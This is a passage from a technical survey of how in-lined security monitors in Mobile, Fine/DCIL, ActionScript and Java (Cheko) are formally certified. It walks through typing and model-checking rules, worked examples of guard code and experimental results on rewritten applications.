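In the version that Hamlen and colleagues published in 2006, the package is a class, and both operations lock the package itself. Two threads using the same package have to take turns, so they can no longer mix up an object and a state value. Making the package a class also stops the copying. Both texts describe the operations as atomic, meaning that no other thread can interrupt them, but only the 2006 code achieves this. This comparison is based on the printed figures, and the code that the researchers ran in 2005 may have been different.

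The proofs could not have exposed the flaw because the formal model has a single thread, in which packing is one indivisible step. Hamlen acknowledges that the corrected code has a practical drawback. If one thread has unpacked an object and another tries to unpack the same package, the second thread gets an exception and stops, even if the original program was safe. He suggests making the second thread wait instead.

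### What Mobile's types leave out

Mobile's types track the order of events but not the values of ordinary variables. Suppose a program opens a file and reads it exactly three times in a loop, under a policy that allows three reads. The typing rule for loops requires the same history map before and after each pass, so the file's entry must contain O followed by any number of Rs. That includes ORRRR, which exceeds the limit, so the checker rejects the program unless the rewriter inserts a guard. If the same three reads were written out without a loop, the checker would accept them with no guards. Hamlen and colleagues mention that a richer logic could reason about the loop counter, but the rewriter would then have to produce harder proofs.

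Another limitation is that the implementation requires every subclass of a security-relevant class to obey the same policy as its parent. To support a different policy for a subclass, the checker would have to detect when converting an object from one class to another could cause a violation.

Mobile also supports only one style of monitor, in which the state value sits next to its object in a package. If a rewriter kept all the state values in a separate array, the checker would reject the resulting program even if the program were safe. As the previous section explained, a policy also cannot relate one object to another, such as a file to its encryptor.

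Unlike the theory, the prototype covers only method calls on objects. Hamlen lists global events, such as the limit of ten network sends per run, as future work. He also considers the prototype's policy notation very hard for people to read, which matters because the policy is trusted.

### Fine and DCIL: carrying proofs in .NET code

Mobile's checker doesn't need proofs because it only compares regular expressions, and an algorithm can always decide those comparisons. Policies that mention roles, permissions and particular emails need a more expressive logic. *Type-preserving Compilation for End-to-end Verification of Security Enforcement* (Chen, Chugh and Swamy, 2010) showed how .NET code could carry proofs in such a logic.

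The source language, Fine, has *refinement types*, which combine an ordinary type with a logical condition. For instance, {f : file | CanRead p f} is the type of files that user p is allowed to read. A function that reads files can require an argument of this type, so the program must establish the condition before each call. The compiler uses Z3, an automatic theorem prover, to find the proofs. It turns each condition into an extra argument that contains the proof, and translates the program into DCIL, an extension of .NET's bytecode. The recipient's type-checker verifies the proofs as part of the code, so the recipient does not need to trust Z3 or most of the compiler.

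Their main example is Lookout, a model email program with plugins. Its policy lets a plugin read an email only if the sender is a friend, and reply only if it has not replied to that email before. Reading an email works as follows:

1. The plugin calls a function that checks whether the current list of facts, s, includes the sender's role as a friend. The function's type guarantees that the answer is true exactly when s includes that fact.
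2. In the branch where the answer is true, the compiler combines this guarantee with the policy rule and the fact that the caller is a plugin. The result is a proof that the plugin may read the email in state s.
3. The plugin passes this proof to the function that reads the email.

As in Mobile, the run-time test makes the proof possible. The facts can also change, so a plugin must not be able to rely on an outdated list. Lookout's monitor therefore issues a token certifying that s is the current state. The token has an *affine* type, which means the program can use it at most once. Sending a reply consumes the token and produces a new one for a state that includes the reply, so the plugin can no longer use the old state to show that it hasn't replied. Mobile gets a similar effect by deleting ℓ from the history map.

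Chen and colleagues proved that DCIL's type system is sound and that the translation from Fine preserves types. They also compiled six programs totalling 1,766 lines. The recipient's checking was fast, taking about four seconds for all six programs and less than seven for a 51-megabyte library of lemmas. But the proofs made the compiled programs about 21 times larger on average, and one component grew by a factor of 53. For that component, they also tried a simple prover they had designed to produce short proofs. It reduced the overhead to roughly a factor of two, but only after they carefully rewrote the code to suit it.

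Fine is less suited than Mobile to existing programs. Programmers write the security-critical code in Fine, including its guards, whereas Mobile was designed for guards that a rewriter adds to someone else's bytecode. Fine also needs the policy at compile time, so a recipient cannot apply a new one to a finished program. DCIL covers only a functional part of .NET's bytecode. Other .NET languages can call Fine code, but .NET's standard verifier does not check the extra types, so a C# program could pass one user's credentials where a Fine function requires another's. Programmers have to avoid exposing such functions, and in 2010 the compiler did not yet check this automatically.

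Chen and colleagues also do not claim that their proof system is logically consistent, because Fine allows unrestricted recursion. A function that never returns can have any type, including the type of a proof of a false statement. This does no harm while the proof remains in the program, since the program would loop forever before reaching the protected call. But they planned to shrink the code by deleting proofs after verification. Deleting a proof that never finishes would let the call go ahead, so the deletion step would first have to establish that every proof it removes terminates.

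## Checking by model-checking: Flash programs in ActionScript

Sridhar and Hamlen built a certifier for ActionScript, the bytecode language of Adobe's Flash, and described it in a 2010 paper, *Model-Checking In-lined Reference Monitors*. The certifier uses abstract interpretation to compute an approximate description of the program's state at every instruction, and model-checking to test those descriptions against the policy. Because the descriptions cover what the monitor's variables can contain, the certifier does not need Mobile's packages.

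### Following every path with approximate values

A model-checker treats a system as a set of states with transitions between them. It visits every state that the system can reach and looks for one that breaks a rule. *Model Checking as Program Verification by Abstract Interpretation* (Baldan, Bruni and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a car at a traffic light. The light is red, yellow or green and the car is stopped or driving, which makes six combinations. Starting from a red light and a stopped car, the model-checker finds that the system can reach five of them. The system is safe because it can't reach the sixth, in which the car drives through a red light.

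Real programs have far too many states for this, since two 32-bit variables alone have 2⁶⁴ possible combinations of values. Abstract interpretation, which Patrick and Radhia Cousot introduced in 1977, makes the search manageable by letting one description stand for many states. Suppose that the analysis describes each variable either by a known integer or as "unknown", and take this loop:

```
1  i = 0
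2  if done: goto 5
3  i = i + 1
4  goto 2
5  ...
```

The analysis first reaches line 2 with `i` equal to 0, then returns after one pass through the loop with `i` equal to 1. It *joins* the two descriptions, replacing them with the smallest description that covers both, here "unknown". On the next pass, adding 1 to an unknown number gives an unknown number, so nothing changes and the analysis stops. A description that stays the same on further passes is a *fixed point*. As *Agentic Interpretation* (2026) explains, the analysis must reach one if a description can grow only a finite number of times. Here each variable's description can grow only once, from known to unknown.

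The final descriptions cover every real run, so if none of them permits a violation, no violation can occur. They may also cover impossible runs, which cause false alarms. *Elusive but Coverable* (2026) notes that abstract interpretation is sound by construction, but that an analysis free of false alarms is rare. Baldan and colleagues produce a false alarm with the traffic light. In their system, a car at a green light is always driving in the next state. But no description in their set covered exactly the two green-light states, so the analysis used a broader one that included a car that might stay stopped.

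### The 2009 prototype

DeVries, Gupta and colleagues had already applied these ideas to ActionScript in a prototype, described in *ActionScript Bytecode Verification With Co-Logic Programming* (2009). They point out that the analysis would be useless for monitors if it described every variable as "unknown", because both outcomes of every guard would look possible and the checker could not establish that a guard prevents anything. Their prototype therefore keeps an exact value wherever it can determine one. This is usually enough for a monitor's variables, because the inserted code sets them to constants.

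The prototype takes policies in linear temporal logic, which adds operators for time to ordinary logic. G means "from now on" and F means "at some point". The policy against sending secrets is:

G(open → G(read → ¬F send))

Once the program has opened a file in the secret directory and then read from a file, it must never send.

DeVries and colleagues wrote the checker in Prolog, a language in which the programmer states rules and the computer searches for proofs. A loop in the checked program can make this search go round forever. Co-logic programming adds two ways of stopping when the search comes back to a question it is already working on:

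- Tabling treats the repetition as no new evidence, so the answer is "no" unless another route supplies a proof. This suits the question of whether the program can ever reach a forbidden send.
- Coinduction treats the repetition as success. This suits the question of whether the program stays within the policy forever. If a loop returns to an earlier state without a violation, it can go round indefinitely without one.

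The tests used three versions of a small program that may read a file, depending on an input the checker cannot know, and then writes to a network socket. The prototype rejected the version without guards in 0.093 seconds. It accepted a guarded version in 0.110 seconds and the same code inside an infinite loop in 0.101 seconds. The parser took about 2,000 lines of code, and the model of ActionScript and the model-checker took about 1,000 each. The prototype could not analyse security-relevant behaviour that involved calls between methods, so it was far from handling real applications.

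### Why the monitor state lags behind

The 2010 certifier takes its policy as a security automaton and expects the monitor to store the automaton's current state as an integer. A program usually can't perform an event and update a variable in the same instruction, though. With the read-and-send policy, there is a moment after the read when the policy state is 1 and the monitor state is still 0. A guard at that moment gives outdated information:

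```
read
if state == 0: send
state = 1
```

The guard passes and the program sends after reading. A certifier that assumed the two states were always equal would accept this code.

Sridhar and Hamlen solve the problem by keeping track of what has happened since the last update. For an automaton state q, let Res(q) be the set of finite traces that take the automaton to q. In the read-and-send policy, Res(0) contains the traces with no read, and Res(1) contains those with at least one read and no send after it. Together they make up P, the set of all permitted traces. At each instruction, the certifier's description has three relevant parts, written here as (m, S, τ):

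- m is the monitor state, or "?" if it is unknown.
- S is the set of states that the automaton might have been in at the last update.
- τ is the list of events since then.

The description covers every trace in Res(S)τ, the set of traces formed by appending τ to a trace in Res(q) for some q in S. In the faulty code above, the description after the read is (0, {0}, read), which correctly combines a monitor state of 0 with a policy state of 1.

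The list can contain at most k events, since a loop could otherwise make it grow forever. If more than k events occur between updates to the monitor's variable, the certifier must use a less precise description and may reject a safe program. A larger k lets the monitor update its variable less often, which can make the program faster, but gives the certifier more descriptions to consider. Sridhar and Hamlen found k = 1 sufficient for their implementation. A list of one event is always enough if the monitor updates its variable immediately after each event.

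### The rules on a small program

Three rules deal with the monitor:

- At an event e, the certifier adds e to the end of every trace in the description. If any resulting trace lies outside P, it rejects the program.
- At an update `state = n`, it requires Res(S)τ ⊆ Res(n), meaning that every possible trace must really lead to state n. The description then becomes (n, {n}, –), where the dash stands for an empty list.
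- At a test `state == n`, it follows the success branch if m is n or unknown, with the description (n, {n}, τ). It follows the failure branch if m is unknown or differs from n, and removes n from S. It keeps τ in both branches, because the test only reveals the state at the last update.

The following program keeps sending a status message and sometimes reads a file. The monitor halts the program if it tries to send a message after reading a file.

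```
1  if state == 0: goto 3         # guard
2  halt
3  send
4  if not wants_report: goto 1
5  read
6  state = 1                     # update
7  goto 1
```

The table gives the description just before each line, first when the certifier initially gets there and then at the fixed point.

| Line | First visit | Fixed point |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | (0, {0}, –) | (?, {0, 1}, –) |
| 2 | not reached | (?, {1}, –) |
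| 3 | (0, {0}, –) | (0, {0}, –) |
| 4 | (0, {0}, –) | (0, {0}, –) |
| 5 | (0, {0}, –) | (0, {0}, –) |
| 6 | (0, {0}, read) | (0, {0}, read) |
| 7 | (1, {1}, –) | (1, {1}, –) |

The send at line 3 leaves the list empty because Res(0) already includes traces that end in a send. At line 6, every trace with no read followed by one read belongs to Res(1), so the update is correct. The jump at line 7 brings (1, {1}, –) back to line 1. Joining it with the earlier description gives (?, {0, 1}, –), which no longer shows whether a read has happened. The guard recovers that information because execution reaches line 3 only if `state` is 0, and a send is permitted in that state. Another pass changes nothing, and the certifier accepts the program.

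Suppose a faulty rewriter writes `state = 0` at line 6. The certifier must show that every trace in Res(0) followed by a read is itself in Res(0). The trace (read) is a counterexample, so the certifier rejects the program. If the program had run, the guard would have allowed the next send after the read.

The update rule also rejects some correct monitors. The rewritten program in the first section of this report sets `state = 1` just before the read. That is safe, but no read has happened when the update runs, so the possible traces are not yet in Res(1). Sridhar and Hamlen list this kind of early update as unsupported.

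### A missing update that the printed rules accept

Deleting line 6 altogether reproduces the fault that the optimizer introduced in the first section. The program can now send, read, return to line 1 with `state` still at 0, pass the guard and send again. The rules as printed accept it:

1. After the read, the description is (0, {0}, read), and the program jumps back to line 1 with it.
2. The certifier joins it with the earlier description of line 1, (0, {0}, –). No description with a monitor state of 0 covers both, since one has a read after the last update and the other doesn't. The smallest one that does is (?, {0, 1}, –).
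3. The guard narrows this to (0, {0}, –), and the certifier permits the send.

The join discards the fact that a read followed the last update, so the test rule treats an outdated monitor state as current. The published soundness proof does not cover this step, because when the monitor state is unknown and the test succeeds, the rule narrows the set of traces but the proof leaves it unchanged. A certifier that followed the proof would reject the faulty program but also the correct one, because it would reach line 3 without having established that no read had happened.

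One fix is to keep descriptions separate when their monitor states or lists differ. The description (0, {0}, read) then reaches the guard intact and passes it, and the event rule rejects the send. The 2009 prototype explored each path independently, and if the 2010 implementation did too, the fault is only in the printed version. Sridhar's 2014 dissertation, also titled *Model-Checking In-lined Reference Monitors*, contains the same rules and proof case. It also reports complete soundness proofs in Coq, a program that checks mathematical proofs. Since the printed rules do not satisfy the theorem, the Coq version presumably states them differently.

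A separate theorem limits how long the analysis can take. If the automaton has |Q| states, the part of a description that covers traces can grow at most O(|Q|² + k|Q|) times at any one instruction. In the worst case, a policy with ten times as many states could therefore need about a hundred times as many passes, but the number does not grow exponentially.

### Redirects in web advertisements

The main experiment dealt with advertisements that send a visitor's browser to another website without permission. ActionScript programs do this by calling `navigateToURL`. The policy required a call to `check_url(s)` at some point before any call to `navigateToURL(s)`. The advertising distributor or the website supplies `check_url`, which can take account of the current page or user. Its code is trusted, so the certificate guarantees that the check comes first but not that it catches every malicious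 address.

A simple monitor would call `check_url` before every redirect, which could be slow. The rewriter instead gave each address written into the program its own state variable, so that the program checked each of those addresses only once. If the program assembled an address while running, the monitor checked it every time.

Sridhar and Hamlen first reported results for two advertisements. A companion paper, *ActionScript In-lined Reference Monitoring in Prolog*, adds two more and tests two other policies on desktop applications. One policy required the program to sanitize text that users typed into message boxes, and the monitor enforced it in Posty, a tool for posting to social networks. The other limited how many files FedEx's parcel-tracking application could create.

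| Program | Policy | Size before | Size after | Rewriting | Certification |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| countdownBadge | redirects | 1.80 KB | 1.95 KB | 1.43 s | 0.53 s |
| NavToURL | redirects | 0.93 KB | 1.03 KB | 0.86 s | 0.23 s |
| fiona | redirects | 58.9 KB | 59.3 KB | 15.88 s | 0.89 s |
| calder | redirects | 58.2 KB | 58.6 KB | 16.33 s | 0.88 s |
| posty | message text | 112.0 KB | 113.0 KB | 54.17 s | 2.44 s |
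| fedex | file limit | 77.3 KB | 78.0 KB | 39.65 s | 1.73 s |

All six programs passed certification. The monitors made the four larger programs less than 1% bigger, and certifying those programs was about 18 to 23 times faster than rewriting them. This suits web advertising, where a distributor can do the slow rewriting once and each recipient only has to run the certifier. The evidence is limited because neither paper measures how much the guards slowed the programs down or reports how the certifier handled output from a deliberately faulty rewriter.

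### Many rewriters and one certifier

Sridhar and Hamlen wrote a separate rewriter for each family of policies so that each could use the most efficient guards for its policies, and they used a single certifier to check all the output.

Each rewriter took about 400 lines of Prolog, and they shared another 900 lines for reading and writing bytecode. The certifier took about 2,000 lines, so for a single family of policies it was much longer than the rewriter that it made unnecessary to trust. Leaving out the shared code, the certifier is shorter than the rewriters combined only when there are more than about five families. Sridhar and Hamlen point out that general-purpose model-checkers, which have no rewriter to simplify their task, are often much larger.

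When the certifier rejects a program, it returns a counterexample. In the 2009 prototype, this was a sequence of instructions leading to a violation, and a developer could use it to find the fault. Because the analysis is approximate, the sequence may be impossible in a real run.

The certifier had gaps besides early updates. It did not handle recursion, where a method calls itself, or monitors that keep a separate state for each object. It also did not support events that only a run-time test can identify, which SPoX policies allow. Sridhar's dissertation concedes that this ruled out real-world monitoring systems and their policies. Cheko later removed several of these restrictions.

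### After Flash

Adobe stopped supporting Flash Player on December 31, 2020, and began blocking Flash content from running in it on January 12, 2021. The ActionScript certifier therefore has no practical use in today's browsers.

Little of the method depends on Flash. The certifier builds its descriptions from the policy's automaton, and the formal model has only seven instructions: two for jumps, two for local variables, and one each for events, updates and tests. To move the method to another bytecode language, a developer would need a new parser and a model of that language's instructions. The language would also have to protect the monitor state, as ActionScript and Java bytecode both do through type safety. Cheko applies the method to Java.

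## Checking Java programs with untrusted hints from the rewriter

The ActionScript certifier could not check a monitor that updates its state before an event, or a policy that depends on an argument known only at run time. Both are common in monitors for SPoX policies. Hamlen, Jones and Sridhar built Cheko (also spelled Chekov) to certify these monitors, and described it in a 2011 report and a shorter 2012 paper. Cheko takes a SPoX policy, a rewritten Java program and hints from the rewriter. It uses the hints to decide where to check the program closely, but does not assume they are correct.

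Like the ActionScript certifier, Cheko computes a description of the program's possible states at each instruction. It writes each description as one or more *constraint lists*, which are sets of equations and inequalities that all hold at the same time, such as "A = S and 0 ≤ S ≤ 9". Cheko drops any list that no values can satisfy, because no run can be in the situation it describes.

### Two hints and an invariant

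Most of a typical program has nothing to do with the policy. JVMail, a small email client that the researchers tested, has two instructions that matter to a limit on emails. Following constraint lists through all the rest would be slow, and the number of lists could get out of hand. The rewriter already knows where it put its guards, so Hamlen and colleagues modified the SPoX rewriter to pass on two pieces of information:

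- which program variables record which of the policy's state variables
- which regions of the code may contain moments when the two are out of step

The first hint defines a condition called SYNC, which holds when every program variable named in the hint equals the policy variable it is meant to record. Let r ∼ s mean that program variable r records policy variable s, and let ζ be the constraints at some point in the program. The program is synchronized at that point if

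ζ ∧ (r ≠ s for at least one pair r ∼ s)

has no solution. In other words, the constraints leave no room for a mismatch.

SYNC then serves as an invariant, a condition that Cheko shows to hold again and again throughout the run:

1. Cheko checks that SYNC holds when the program starts.
2. It scans the unmarked code once, to confirm that this code contains no security-relevant events and never writes to the monitor's variables. Such code cannot disturb SYNC.
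3. It analyses each marked region separately. It assumes SYNC at the entrance and follows every path with constraint lists. No list may permit a violation, and SYNC must hold again at every exit.

Together these checks cover the whole run. The program enters its first marked region in SYNC, leaves it in SYNC without a violation, stays in SYNC until the next region, and so on. Between regions, Cheko can discard everything except SYNC.

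A false hint cannot make this argument succeed for an unsafe program, because the hints only propose what Cheko should try to prove. If the rewriter fails to mark a region that sends email, the scan finds the event in unmarked code and Cheko rejects the program. If it marks a region that has nothing to do with the policy, Cheko takes longer because it analyses that region in detail. If it names the wrong variable, say one that holds the size of the inbox, Cheko tries to prove that the inbox size always equals the number of emails sent. The proof fails as soon as new mail arrives in unmarked code.

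This reasoning about hints is informal. The formal model in the 2011 report has only five kinds of instruction and no marked regions, so its soundness theorem covers the constraint lists but not the shortcut that the hints allow.

### The ten-email monitor, list by list

Hamlen and colleagues demonstrate Cheko on the policy that allows at most ten emails per run. The SPoX rewriter puts code like this around each call that sends an email:

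```
1  if s >= 0 and s <= 9:
2      temp_s = s + 1
3  if s == 10:
4      exit
5  s = temp_s
6  Mail.send()
```

The monitor keeps its count in `s` but calculates the new value in `temp_s` so that the two tests don't interfere with each other. If line 2 changed `s` directly, the tenth call would raise `s` from 9 to 10, and line 3 would stop the program one email too early.

Let A be the policy state, S the value of `s` and T the value of `temp_s`. The hint links both variables to the policy state, so SYNC is A = S and A = T. All six lines form one marked region. The test at line 1 splits the analysis into two branches, shown here without constraints that no longer matter. S′ is the value of `s` before line 5 changed it.

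| Point in the code | Line 1's test succeeds | Line 1's test fails |
|---|---|---|
| Before line 1 | A = S, A = T | A = S, A = T |
| After the test at line 1 | adds 0 ≤ S ≤ 9 | adds S < 0 or S > 9 |
| After line 2 | A = S, 0 ≤ S ≤ 9, T = S + 1 | line 2 does not run |
| At line 4 | adds S = 10, a contradiction | adds S = 10, and the program exits |
| Before line 5 | adds S ≠ 10 | adds S ≠ 10 |
| After line 5 | A = S′, 0 ≤ S′ ≤ 9, S = T = S′ + 1 | A = S′ = T = S, S′ < 0 or S′ > 9, S′ ≠ 10 |

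After line 5, the monitor state in the first branch is one ahead of the policy state, because the monitor has counted an email that the program has not sent yet. The ActionScript certifier rejected this kind of early update, but Cheko records the difference and continues.

At line 6 the program sends the email and the policy state may change. Write A′ for the policy state before the call and A for the state after it. The policy allows for three cases:

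- If A′ is between 0 and 9, the call is permitted and A = A′ + 1.
- If A′ is 10, the call is a violation, written A = #.
- If A′ is anything else, no rule applies and A = A′.

Cheko tries each case with each branch, which gives six lists. The numbers are those that Hamlen and colleagues use.

| List | Line 1's test | Policy case | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| 6.1 | succeeded | counted | possible, with A = S = T |
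| 6.2 | succeeded | violation | contradiction: S′ ≤ 9, but A′ = S′ = 10 |
| 6.3 | succeeded | no rule | contradiction: S′ is in 0–9, but A′ = S′ is outside 0–10 |
| 6.4 | failed | counted | contradiction: S′ is outside 0–9, but A′ = S′ is inside it |
| 6.5 | failed | violation | contradiction: S′ ≠ 10, but A′ = S′ = 10 |
| 6.6 | failed | no rule | possible, with A = S = T |

Both lists that describe a violation, 6.2 and 6.5, are contradictory. In the remaining two lists, A, S and T are all equal, so SYNC holds again at the exit and Cheko accepts the region.

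List 6.6 describes a count below 0 or above 10. No real run reaches such a count, because the count starts at 0 and stops at 10, but SYNC as defined here doesn't include these limits. The leftover list is harmless because the policy has no rule against sending an email in such a state. A rewriter can also propose a more informative invariant. The synchronization condition for the same policy in Hamlen's lecture slides, *Model-Checking In-lined Reference Monitors*, includes s ≤ 10.

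Deleting lines 3 and 4, the test for 10, removes the constraint S′ ≠ 10 from both branches and makes list 6.5 satisfiable, with A′, S and T all equal to 10. These values correspond to the eleventh email, for which line 1's test fails, line 5 copies 10 over 10, and line 6 sends the message. Cheko rejects the program because one satisfiable list containing A = # is enough for a rejection. Hamlen and colleagues write in the 2012 paper that list 6.2 also becomes satisfiable, but it remains contradictory because line 1's test still requires S′ ≤ 9 there.

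The policy's ten counting transitions add only one list to each branch because Cheko represents all ten with a single unknown number I between 0 and 9. In general, an event that could match m of the policy's rules turns n lists into at most n(m + 1). Here two lists and two rules give six, even if the limit were ten thousand emails. The ActionScript certifier tracked sets of individual automaton states, so its descriptions could grow with the limit.

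### Arguments that only the running program knows

Some policies restrict the arguments a program passes to a method. Sridhar and Hamlen had found it hard to express realistic policies of this kind as types, which is one reason they preferred model-checking to Mobile's approach. Cheko handles numeric arguments by adding the program's own numeric variables to the constraint lists.

The 2011 report gives a short example with a policy that forbids calling `secure_method` with an argument greater than 2:

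```
1  x = 1
2  if s == 0 and x > 2:
3      exit
4  secure_method(x)
```

Let X be the value of `x`. The policy starts in state 0, and a call in that state with X > 2 is a violation. At line 4, Cheko can infer from line 1 that X = 1, so the violation is impossible and the guard isn't needed.

If `x` comes from the user instead, the guard becomes essential, because Cheko has no constraints on X after line 1. If execution gets past the guard, the test at line 2 failed, so either S ≠ 0 or X ≤ 2. A violation at line 4 would need A = 0 and X > 2. Since A = S, S would also be 0, so X ≤ 2 would have to hold, which contradicts X > 2. Cheko therefore accepts the call for any value the user types.

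Text is harder to put into equations. A policy might forbid file names that match a pattern such as "ends in .exe". For each text variable x and each pattern p in the policy, Cheko introduces a number that is 1 if x matches p and 0 if it does not. When the program tests x against p, Cheko constrains this number to be 1 in the branch for a match and 0 in the other branch. Cheko checks only that the program made the right test and acted on the result, without examining the text itself. It would presumably not accept a guard that used a different but stricter pattern, because it cannot compare two patterns.

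### Tests on 24 applications

Hamlen and colleagues rewrote and certified 24 Java applications. They used JVMail with two different policies, which makes 25 runs. The 2011 report divides the policies into eight classes:

| Class | Runs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| File names | 5 | The text editor RText may not save files with executable extensions |
| Order of events | 3 | A weather widget may not send data over the network after accessing the Windows directory |
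| Pop-up windows | 1 | A file-encryption tool may not open its window |
| Network ports | 3 | A remote-terminal program may use only ports 20 to 29 |
| Resource limits | 5 | JVMail may send at most ten emails |
| Freeriding | 2 | A file-sharing program's downloads may exceed its uploads by at most two |
| Malicious input | 3 | Fields in the web application Webgoat may contain only approved characters |
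| Required steps | 3 | JVMail must encrypt and then log each email before sending it |

For the last class, the researchers inserted the encryption and logging calls into JVMail by hand. Cheko then checked the finished program against a policy about the order of the calls. A customer could add custom enforcement code this way without trusting it. But the certificate covers only what the policy mentions. The printed policy names the three methods but not their arguments, so a program that encrypted one message and sent another would pass.

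The printed policy also has a mistake that certification could not reveal. It keeps one variable for "encrypted" and another for "logged", and sending an email resets only the first. When the program tries to encrypt its next email, the call counts as coming after logging, which is a violation, so the printed policy allows only one email per run. Hamlen and colleagues describe it as a simplified version, so the policy they used in the test may have been correct.

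All 25 runs eventually passed certification. These are the times for the quickest run, the median run, the slowest run and one with especially large libraries, all on a laptop:

| Program | Program size | Libraries checked | Rewriting | Total certification | Model-checking only |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| JVMail, ten emails (quickest) | 25 KB | none | 1.6 s | 35.1 s | 8.0 s |
| jfilecrypt (median) | 303 KB | none | 9.7 s | 642.2 s | 2.8 s |
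| OpenMRS, a medical database | 1,783 KB | 24,279 KB | 78.7 s | 2,897 s | 37.3 s |
| Webgoat (slowest) | 431 KB | 6,338 KB | 16.7 s | 10,876 s | 120 s |
| Average of all 25 runs | | | 32.4 s | 1,846.6 s | 45.2 s |

Webgoat took about three hours, including two minutes of model-checking. Across all the runs, model-checking made up about 2.5% of the total time. Hamlen and colleagues attribute much of the rest to how they built the prototype. Its parser, abstract interpreter and model-checker were separate modules, partly in Java and partly in Prolog, and switching between them was slow. Cheko also had to scan all the unmarked code, including library code.

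They did not publish a breakdown of the remaining time, so it is unclear how much of that time a better implementation could save. Code size alone doesn't explain the differences in certification time. OpenMRS has almost four times as much library code as Webgoat, but Cheko certified it in about a quarter of the time.

The model-checking times are encouraging for the method. The longest was 196 seconds, for an editor of hieroglyphic texts with over 20 megabytes of libraries. Webgoat's policy tested twelve arguments at a single call, which could have multiplied the number of lists, but Hamlen and colleagues found that Cheko combined enough redundant constraints to keep the time roughly proportional to code size.

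The prototype would not work well as a product, however, because the recipient has to run the slower step. Unlike with the ActionScript tools, certification took longer than rewriting in every run, and about 57 times as long on average. A recipient would have to wait half an hour to certify a typical large application, unless the overhead between modules could be avoided.

The 2012 paper reports the same times as the 2011 report but different sizes for the original programs. According to the report, the file-renaming tool vrenamer shrank from 1,048 to 927 KB when the rewriter added a monitor, because the rewriter also removes unneeded metadata from Java files. The paper gives vrenamer's original size as 924 KB, so the monitor adds 3 KB. The paper's figures seem to exclude the metadata, so they better reflect the monitors' size. By those figures, no program grew by more than 6 KB. Neither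 publication measures how much the monitors slowed the programs down.

### What went wrong with vrenamer

One policy forbade vrenamer to give files executable extensions. The SPoX rewriter inserted the guards, and Cheko rejected the result.

The researchers examined the bytecode and traced the problem to an exception handler in the original program. When something goes wrong in a Java program, the code can throw an exception, which makes execution jump to the nearest handler that accepts it. vrenamer had a global handler that caught exceptions from a large part of the program, including the part where the rewriter had inserted its guard code. If the guard code threw an exception, this handler would catch it, and execution would continue elsewhere without finishing the guard code.

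The read-and-send policy from the first section shows how this could lead to a violation. Suppose a rewriter produced the following code:

```
try:
    text = read(file)
    ...                      # inserted code that may throw an exception
    state = 1                # inserted
catch any exception:
    show an error message

if state != 0: halt          # inserted
send(status)
```

Normally the program halts before the send. But if the inserted code on the third line throws an exception, execution jumps over `state = 1` to the handler. The program has read the file, but `state` is still 0, so the guard allows the send. Testing could easily miss this, because the flaw appears only when that line throws.

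Cheko treats the jump to the handler as another exit from the marked region. At that exit the policy state is 1 and the monitor state is 0, so SYNC does not hold and Cheko rejects the program. Hamlen and colleagues say vrenamer's handler could put the two states out of sync in this way, but they do not report a run in which it did.

They concluded that the rewriter was at fault because it had not protected its guards from the program's existing handlers. For the experiment, they edited the rewritten bytecode by hand to move the guard code out of the handler's reach, and Cheko then accepted it. They suggest that the rewriter could do this automatically by giving each guard its own handler inside the program's. The 2011 report mentions the problem only for vrenamer. The 2012 paper lists six applications that Cheko rejected for the same reason, including Webgoat and the weather widget, so the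 flaw affected a quarter of the applications tested.

The case is a useful guide to interpreting a rejection. vrenamer was not malicious, and its own code was not at fault. Cheko's verdict meant only that it could not prove the rewritten program safe, and someone still had to find out why. The first step is to see which check failed:

- If the scan found an event or a write to the monitor state in unmarked code, the rewriter either forgot a guard or gave a bad hint.
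- If a list containing a violation was satisfiable, its values describe the situation to investigate, such as an eleventh email with the count at 10.
- If SYNC did not hold at an exit, the path to that exit shows where the monitor lost track.

The next step is to check whether a real run could follow that path. If so, the rewriter has a bug, and other programs it has rewritten may have the same problem. If not, the rejection is conservative, and the usual remedy is to add a guard that makes the proof easier. For vrenamer, the path appeared possible from the code.

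The repair was also safe. Manual changes to security code usually require trusting the person who makes them, but this one did not, because Cheko checked the edited bytecode from scratch.

Cheko found a flaw that the rewriter's developers had missed, which is stronger evidence for certification than the ActionScript tests provided. Hamlen and colleagues tested Cheko with only one rewriter, though they expect it to work with others that supply the same hints.

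### Monitors that Cheko cannot certify

Cheko needs an invariant that it can express as linear constraints, but some correct monitors have none. Suppose a monitor enforces a separate limit for each open file and keeps the counts in a hash table, which calculates where to store each entry from its key. To certify this monitor, Cheko would have to show that the table always returns the right count for each file, even when two keys lead to the same place, which its constraint language cannot express.

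Cheko also requires the monitor's variables to be private static fields, which exist once per program rather than once per object. This suited the policies in the experiments, which all concerned a whole run of the program. Mobile tracked every object separately but did not track the values of ordinary variables.

The fields have to be private because other code could otherwise change them. Reflection could bypass this protection by changing fields by name. Cheko accepts most uses of reflection, but rejects a program if a class that holds monitor variables also uses reflection to write to fields. A program may still use reflection to read the monitor state and behave differently when it detects a monitor, but it cannot break the policy by doing so.

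Loops are another restriction. To spare the rewriter from writing more hints, Cheko uses SYNC as the invariant for every loop and every recursive call. The monitor must therefore be synchronized each time the program goes round. Consider a monitor that checks the limit once for three emails:

```
if s > 7: exit
repeat 3 times:
    Mail.send()
s = s + 3
```

The code is safe, but after the first email the policy state is one ahead of `s`, so SYNC fails at the end of the first pass and Cheko rejects the program. Moving the update into the loop would restore SYNC, but Cheko carries only SYNC from one pass to the next. It would lose the fact that `s` was at most 7 at the start, so it couldn't rule out an eleventh email. The rewriter therefore has to put the test inside the loop too, where it runs three times instead of once.

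Guards in inner loops caused most of the runtime overhead in the Mobile experiments. Hamlen and colleagues proposed letting the rewriter supply a different invariant as a hint for each loop, but they knew of no rewriter that could compute them.

Within a marked region, the number of constraint lists can grow exponentially with the length of the code. Each independent test can double it, so ten tests in a row could produce 1,024 lists before the program reaches an event. The researchers did not find this a problem in practice, because rewriters usually insert guards in short, scattered blocks. A rewriter that marked a whole large method would lose this advantage. Here too, the proposed solution is a richer hint, which would identify information that Cheko can safely discard at a given point.

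Finally, Cheko does not support multithreaded programs, because its constraint lists assume that nothing happens between one instruction and the next. In the 2011 report, Hamlen and colleagues thought that support for threads would require a standard analysis for detecting conflicts between threads. A year later they described multithreaded monitors as a subject of continuing research with several open problems. Sridhar's 2014 dissertation, *Model-Checking In-lined Reference Monitors*, repeats that assessment and still lists all of these limits.

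## Shipping a proof with the program

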